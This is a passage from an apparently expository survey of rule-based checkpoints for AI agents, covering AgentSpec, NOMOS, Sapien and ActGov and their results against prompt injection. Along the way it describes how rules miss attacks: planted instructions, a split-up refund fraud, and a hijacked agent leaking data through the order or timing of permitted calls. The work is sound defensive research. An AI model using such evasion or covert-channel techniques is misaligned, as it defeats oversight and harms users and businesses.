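None of these guarantees relies on the agent's main model behaving well, but several rely on software far too large for the complete analysis that Anderson's panel demanded. The Linux kernel has tens of millions of lines of code, although any one machine uses only part of it. Machine-checked proofs reduce the amount of code that people have to trust without proof, but people still have to trust the operating system and hardware underneath.

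KAIROS blocks routes around the checkpoint by giving the virtual machine no other channels. The language and framework designs need something outside them to block those routes. Hempel and colleagues consider checks at the tool interface and checks at the machine boundary complementary.

The refund company could combine them by running the agent in a virtual machine whose only network connection leads to a separate checkpoint program. That program would hold the payment key, accept only typed requests, and forward queries to the language model. The machine boundary would only have to block every other connection, without interpreting any traffic. The checkpoint would receive the order and the amount as fields, so it could apply the 500-dollar limit. A script that tried to contact the payment provider directly would fail because it would have no connection to the provider and no payment key.

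## Where the rules come from and what they miss

A checkpoint can apply the 500-dollar limit only if the limit is in a form it can execute. Developers can write such rules by hand, a compiler can extract them from company documents, or a language model can generate them for each task. The checkpoint reliably enforces whatever rule it is given, even a bad one.

### Rules written by hand

Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, present a small language for handwritten rules. Each rule has a trigger, conditions and a response. The company's limit might look like this:

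```
rule @large_refund
trigger issue_refund
check
    amount_over_500
    !staff_approved
enforce
    user_inspection
end
```

Just before a call to `issue_refund`, AgentSpec checks whether the amount is over 500 dollars and lacks staff approval. If so, it pauses the agent and asks the user. In a customer chat the user is the customer, so the company would have to redirect the question to staff. AgentSpec can instead stop the agent, run a fixed action or have the model reconsider.

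The conditions in an AgentSpec rule are Python functions that receive the user's request and the run so far. Much of what the rule means is therefore in that code and not in the rule's text. If `amount_over_500` compares dollars with a limit in cents, the rule looks correct but isn't triggered by a 640-dollar refund. AgentSpec's parser checks only the form of a rule, so whoever writes the rule has to test whether it does what the company intended.

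Wang and colleagues wrote rules from the risk descriptions in RedCode-Exec, a benchmark of 750 risky instructions for coding agents, and tested them on the same benchmark. The rules flagged 333 of the 422 programs the agent tried to run, or 79 percent. Excluding two categories in which the agent's code did not contain the intended fault, they flagged 91 percent. The researchers judged 58 of the flagged programs harmless. In a second test, with simulated household robots, the rules prevented every hazardous task and reduced completion of safe tasks from 58.6 to 54.3 percent. The researchers knew the risks when they wrote the rules, so these results provide little evidence about unforeseen ones.

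OpenAI's o1 model also wrote rules from examples. On new cases, its rules caught 87 percent of the risky programs. For the robots, 96 percent of the rules' interventions were correct, but the rules missed 29 percent of the hazards.

### Rules compiled from company documents

Many companies already have a written policy. Yu, Kim and Choi (2026), in *NOMOS*, describe a compiler that turns such a document into rules for tool calls. It splits the document into clauses, and a language model proposes rules for each one. The refund company's policy might produce this rule:

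```
type:       precondition
tool:       issue_refund
condition:  small_or_staff_approved
clause:     "A person must approve any refund above 500 dollars."
```

A precondition blocks the tool until the condition is true, so missing information leads to a refusal. The model can only choose conditions from a list that people prepared, with code for each entry. If nobody had written `small_or_staff_approved`, NOMOS could not express the limit. The conditions use only tool results and the user's own messages, so the agent can't satisfy one by claiming that staff approved a refund.

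NOMOS runs the model five times, keeps the rules that most runs produce, and uses ordinary code to look for defects. A model might apply a requirement to every tool, including the ones needed to meet it. Yu and colleagues found this fault in a rule from a shop's policy. The rule required customers to prove their identity first but also blocked the two tools that check identity. Other proposed rules used arguments that the tool did not have. In a test without the defect checks, 8 of 14 airline rules and 3 of 5 retail rules could not work.

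These checks cannot establish that a rule means the same as the policy clause it came from, so NOMOS also replays recorded runs of an unrestricted agent against the rules. One telecom policy requires checking that a bill is overdue before requesting payment, but the model had turned this into a ban on requesting payment while a bill is overdue. In the replay, this rule blocked 47 of the 49 payment requests in successful runs.

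Yu and colleagues tested NOMOS on τ²-bench, the customer-service benchmark, with the open model gemma-4-26B as the agent:

| | Airline, no rules | Airline, NOMOS | Retail, no rules | Retail, NOMOS |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Changes to data that broke the policy | 66.3% | 2.6% | 30.8% | 6.9% |
| Tasks completed | 39.2% | 47.6% | 52.4% | 50.2% |

The differences in completed tasks could be due to chance, but the airline agent became more consistent. Its estimated rate of completing a task three times in a row rose from 23 to 37 percent, a statistically significant gain. The violation rates are based on a strict reading of the policy, which requires a separate confirmation for every change. If one "yes" can cover several announced changes, the violation rates without rules fall to 36.8 percent for the airline and 13.6 percent for retail.

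In the retail test, NOMOS produced no rule for the clause in the shop's policy that restricts which card or account may receive a refund. The separate handwritten checker that measured violations also missed some refunds that broke this clause, until an audit exposed the gap. After Yu and colleagues corrected the checker for this clause and one other, the measured violation rate with NOMOS rose from 3.3 to 6.9 percent.

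AgentDojo has no written policies, so Yu and colleagues wrote a one-page policy for each of its settings. In banking, the compiled rules cut successful attacks from 46.5 percent to zero, while the share of tasks completed when there was no attack fell from 79.2 to 70.8 percent. In Slack, successful attacks fell from 70.5 percent to zero, but task completion fell from 90.5 to 14.3 percent. The Slack rules allowed the agent to use only channels, people and links that the user had named, but ordinary Slack tasks often involve others that the agent finds by reading messages.

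### Rules generated for each task

Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Sapien*, argue that a general-purpose agent needs different rules for each task. Permission to send money is necessary for a refund but dangerous when the user only wants a summary of the inbox. In their system, a language model writes a policy from the user's request and the tools' documentation before the agent starts. If a staff member writes "Refund order 7731 in full and email the customer", the policy might be:

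```
read_order(order_id="7731")@order
  . issue_refund(order_id="7731", amount=PREDICATE(is_total))
  . send_email(to=PREDICATE(is_customer))

def is_total(amount):  return amount == order.result["total"]
def is_customer(to):   return to == order.result["customer"]
```

The dots mean "then", and `@order` stores the result of the lookup for later checks. The agent can refund exactly 640 dollars, once, after reading the order. A fake staff note can't make it refund a different order.

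The model that writes the policy does not receive emails or web pages, so text planted there can't influence it. The exception is a request such as "do the tasks on my list", for which Sapien leaves a gap in the policy and fills it after the agent fetches the list. An attacker who can edit the list can therefore change the rules.

This policy lacks the 500-dollar limit because the limit appears in neither the request nor the tool documentation. Tiffany and colleagues suggest adding a separate confirmation policy for such cases.

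The model that writes a policy also reviews it against a checklist, and no person has to read it. To test the policies, Tiffany and colleagues assumed a worst case, much as Zhou and colleagues did for ELBA. They supposed that an attacker fully controlled the agent and checked whether each policy allowed any sequence of calls that would achieve the attacker's goal. They used two Gemini models (3.8 Flash and 3.1 Pro) and two Claude models (Sonnet 5 and Opus 5).

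On AgentDojo, Sapien's policies ruled out 93 to 95 percent of 949 attacks, depending on the model, while a simple list of permitted tools ruled out 83 to 87 percent. Agents completed one to five fewer of the 97 tasks with a policy than without one. Toolathlon has longer tasks, and Tiffany and colleagues gave the attacker goals that use the same tools as the task. Sapien ruled out 65 percent of 212 attacks on Toolathlon with Gemini 3.8 Flash, and the tool list ruled out 32 percent. Writing and checking the policies raised the average time per Toolathlon task from 548 to 679 seconds.

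On each benchmark, more than four-fifths of the attacks that remained possible depended on the meaning of text, such as the content of an email to a permitted recipient. On Toolathlon, the other 16 percent were possible because a policy was looser than necessary. For example, some policies specified the directory for a new file but not its name.

### Checks that raised task success

Safety checks often make agents less useful, but *Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) describes a case in which the checks helped. The airline tools in τ²-bench carry out any well-formed call, even one that the airline's policy forbids. In 78 percent of GPT-4o mini's failures, the database ended up wrong and no tool reported an error.

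Reddy and colleagues wrote four checks in Python that read the database before a change. They test whether a reservation qualifies for cancellation, whether the baggage charge is right, whether the number of passengers stays the same, and whether the agent has read the record it is about to change. If a check fails, the agent receives the reason and can try something else.

With the checks, GPT-4o mini's success rate rose from 29.6 to 42.0 percent over 250 runs, and a repeat with 750 runs gave almost the same gain. The share of tasks it completed in all five attempts rose from 8 to 26 percent. GPT-5.2 improved from 61.2 to 71.6 percent, though nobody repeated that test. The gains probably arise because the benchmark scores the final state of the database, so a forbidden change often fails the task, and blocking it gives the agent a chance to recover. The checks also protect against false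 claims. In one task, a customer lies to get a cancellation. Agents with the checks succeeded in all 16 runs, and agents without them succeeded at most once in 16.

The checks failed in several ways:

- The baggage check was wrong in 40 of the 42 cases in which it blocked a call.
- In one task, GPT-4o mini kept running into the same refusal and failed all five runs.
- In three tasks, the checks made GPT-5.2 do worse.
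- In the retail setting, where the tools already reject many forbidden calls, the number of successful runs fell from 40 to 37 out of 64. A coding mistake that blocked corrected retries explains much of the drop.

If a check crashes, the system allows the call, which would be a poor choice for payments. Reddy and colleagues wrote the checks for the same tasks they tested on, so the gain may be smaller on new tasks.

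The agents might have improved only because a refusal made them reconsider. *Think Before You Act* (2026) tests this on the same airline tasks. GPT-4.1 completed 50 percent of them without checks and 68 percent with checks in code. When the system objected once to every change without examining it, the rate stayed at 50 percent. But for gpt-oss-120b, such objections helped as much as a full set of checks, so the explanation may differ between models.

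### Harm that the rules permit

A rule can work as written and still miss a mistake. For example, a 400-dollar refund on the wrong order satisfies the 500-dollar rule. In *Think Before You Act*, 42 of 101 incorrect calls broke none of the compiled rules, because those rules covered the airline's policy but not the customer's request.

Rules can also rely on the wrong data. The NOMOS banking rules allow payments to anyone in the account's transaction history. Yu and colleagues point out that an attacker could get into that history by sending the account holder some money. Their tests did not cover this trick, but the agents did pay people already in the history when an attacker requested it. With Llama 3.3 70B as the agent, this happened in 11 of 140 attack runs. In one, the user had only asked a question, and the agent sent four instalments of $10,000.

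Harm can also build up from steps that are individually acceptable. *Local Allow, Global Deny* (2026) calls this a "compositional authorization failure". Suppose someone opens three accounts with the refund company, places twelve orders of 450 dollars each, and falsely reports every item as broken. The agent handles each complaint in a separate run and pays out 5,400 dollars in total, although no refund exceeds 500 dollars and no order is refunded twice.

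A monitor that follows one run cannot catch this, because each run contains a single refund. A rule that uses the company's whole ledger could limit the total refunded to each card. The second refund to the same card would bring the total to 900 dollars, and the runtime would hold that refund for staff. This rule also fails if the fraudster pays for every order with a different card. A daily limit on all refunds would eventually stop the fraud, but it would also block refunds to honest customers after the company ships a faulty batch.

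Tracking where data came from does not help here, because the amount and the card come from the company's own database and the lie is in the customer's complaint. Blocking all refunds prompted by customers' emails would prevent the fraud, but it would also block the legitimate refunds among them.

Data tracking is more useful against leaks. *Securing Multi-Tool AI Agent Chains With Dynamic, Real-Time Compositional Policies* (2026) gives the example of an agent that reads an internal document with one permitted tool and posts it to an outside server with another. At the refund company, a stranger might ask where order 7731 is going, and the agent might look it up and reply with the buyer's home address. A rule that order details may go only to the buyer would block the reply. The rule works best if data keeps its label when a model rewords it, as in CaMeL. KAIROS compares text, so it could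 miss a reworded address.

| Rule | Twelve refunds of 450 dollars | Address sent to a stranger |
|---|---|---|
| Limit on each refund | Missed | Missed |
| Limit on the total for each order | Missed | Missed |
| Limit on the total for each card, across all runs | Caught if a card repeats | Missed |
| Amount and card must come from the order database | Missed | Missed |
| Order details may go only to the buyer | Missed | Caught if labels survive rewording |

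Some policies can be checked only by comparing runs. For example, the company might require that two customers with the same complaint get the same treatment. Each run looks fine alone, and a ledger allows the comparison only if both customers actually wrote in. In *Local Allow, Global Deny*, nine language models approved almost every action when they judged it separately but flagged the problem when shown both runs, so a better judge of single actions would not have been enough.

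### Words, silence and side channels

A refund agent can do harm without requesting a refund. It might tell a customer with a valid claim that the company never refunds opened laptops, and a limit on payments would not prevent this. One AgentDojo attack, which is meant only to make the agent output a particular sentence, accounts for 36 percent of the attacks that remained possible under Sapien. An attacker can also persuade an agent to stop working, which breaks no rule about tool calls.

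A rule can inspect replies if they pass through the checkpoint, but judging whether a sentence is true is much harder than comparing 640 with 500. Sapien can send another language model a narrow question, such as whether an email accurately summarises a document. Planted text might fool that model, but the policy's other conditions still apply.

A hijacked agent can also leak information through the timing or order of permitted calls. If a policy allows ten different lookups in any order, the agent can arrange them in 3,628,800 ways, enough to encode any six-digit number. The attacker would need a way to observe the lookups, for example by controlling the service that receives them. A policy that fixes the order prevents leaks through ordering but not through timing, and it makes the agent less flexible.

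### Reviewing and improving the rules

The main reply to these objections is that people can read explicit rules, find the mistakes and correct them. NOMOS stores the source clause with each rule, so a reviewer can look for clauses that have no rule. In the retail test, two missing clauses accounted for 21 of the 40 remaining violations. In their audit, Reddy and colleagues likewise identified the baggage check as the one to revise.

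A short list of rules can also cover many attacks. AgentDojo's banking setting has nine attacker goals, and seven of them depend on who receives the money. Three NOMOS rules therefore blocked every call that would have paid the attacker or set the attacker's password, however the planted text was worded.

*ActGov* (Zhang, Peng and colleagues, 2026) combines generated rules with formal checks and human review. GPT-5.5 proposes rules from tool descriptions, harmless runs and past attacks. Z3, a program that solves logical formulas, then searches for a combination of facts under which the rules would violate a safety requirement. For example, Z3 might find that the refund company's rules allow a refund over 500 without approval. GPT-5.5 revises the rules until Z3 finds no such case, and administrators review the result. The search covers only a fixed set of facts, such as whether an argument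 came from an untrusted source. A language model supplies some of these facts during a run, so its mistakes can still lead to wrong decisions.

In ActGov's AgentDojo tests, no attack succeeded against any of four models, but with DeepSeek-v4-pro as the agent, the share of tasks completed fell from 87.8 to 75.5 percent. On AgentDyn, the agent completed 60 percent of tasks with rules developed for that benchmark, but only 10 percent with rules developed for AgentDojo. The AgentDojo rules still stopped every attack there, mostly by blocking too much. Because rules developed for one set of tasks can work so poorly on another, a company would have to revise its rules whenever the agent's work changes.

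Asking staff to read a new Sapien policy for every task would also bring back approval fatigue. The refund company could instead have people review only its lasting rules, such as the 500-dollar limit and the total for each card, and require every call to satisfy both those rules and the generated policy. A bad generated policy could then block a legitimate refund, but it could not permit one that the company's rules forbid.
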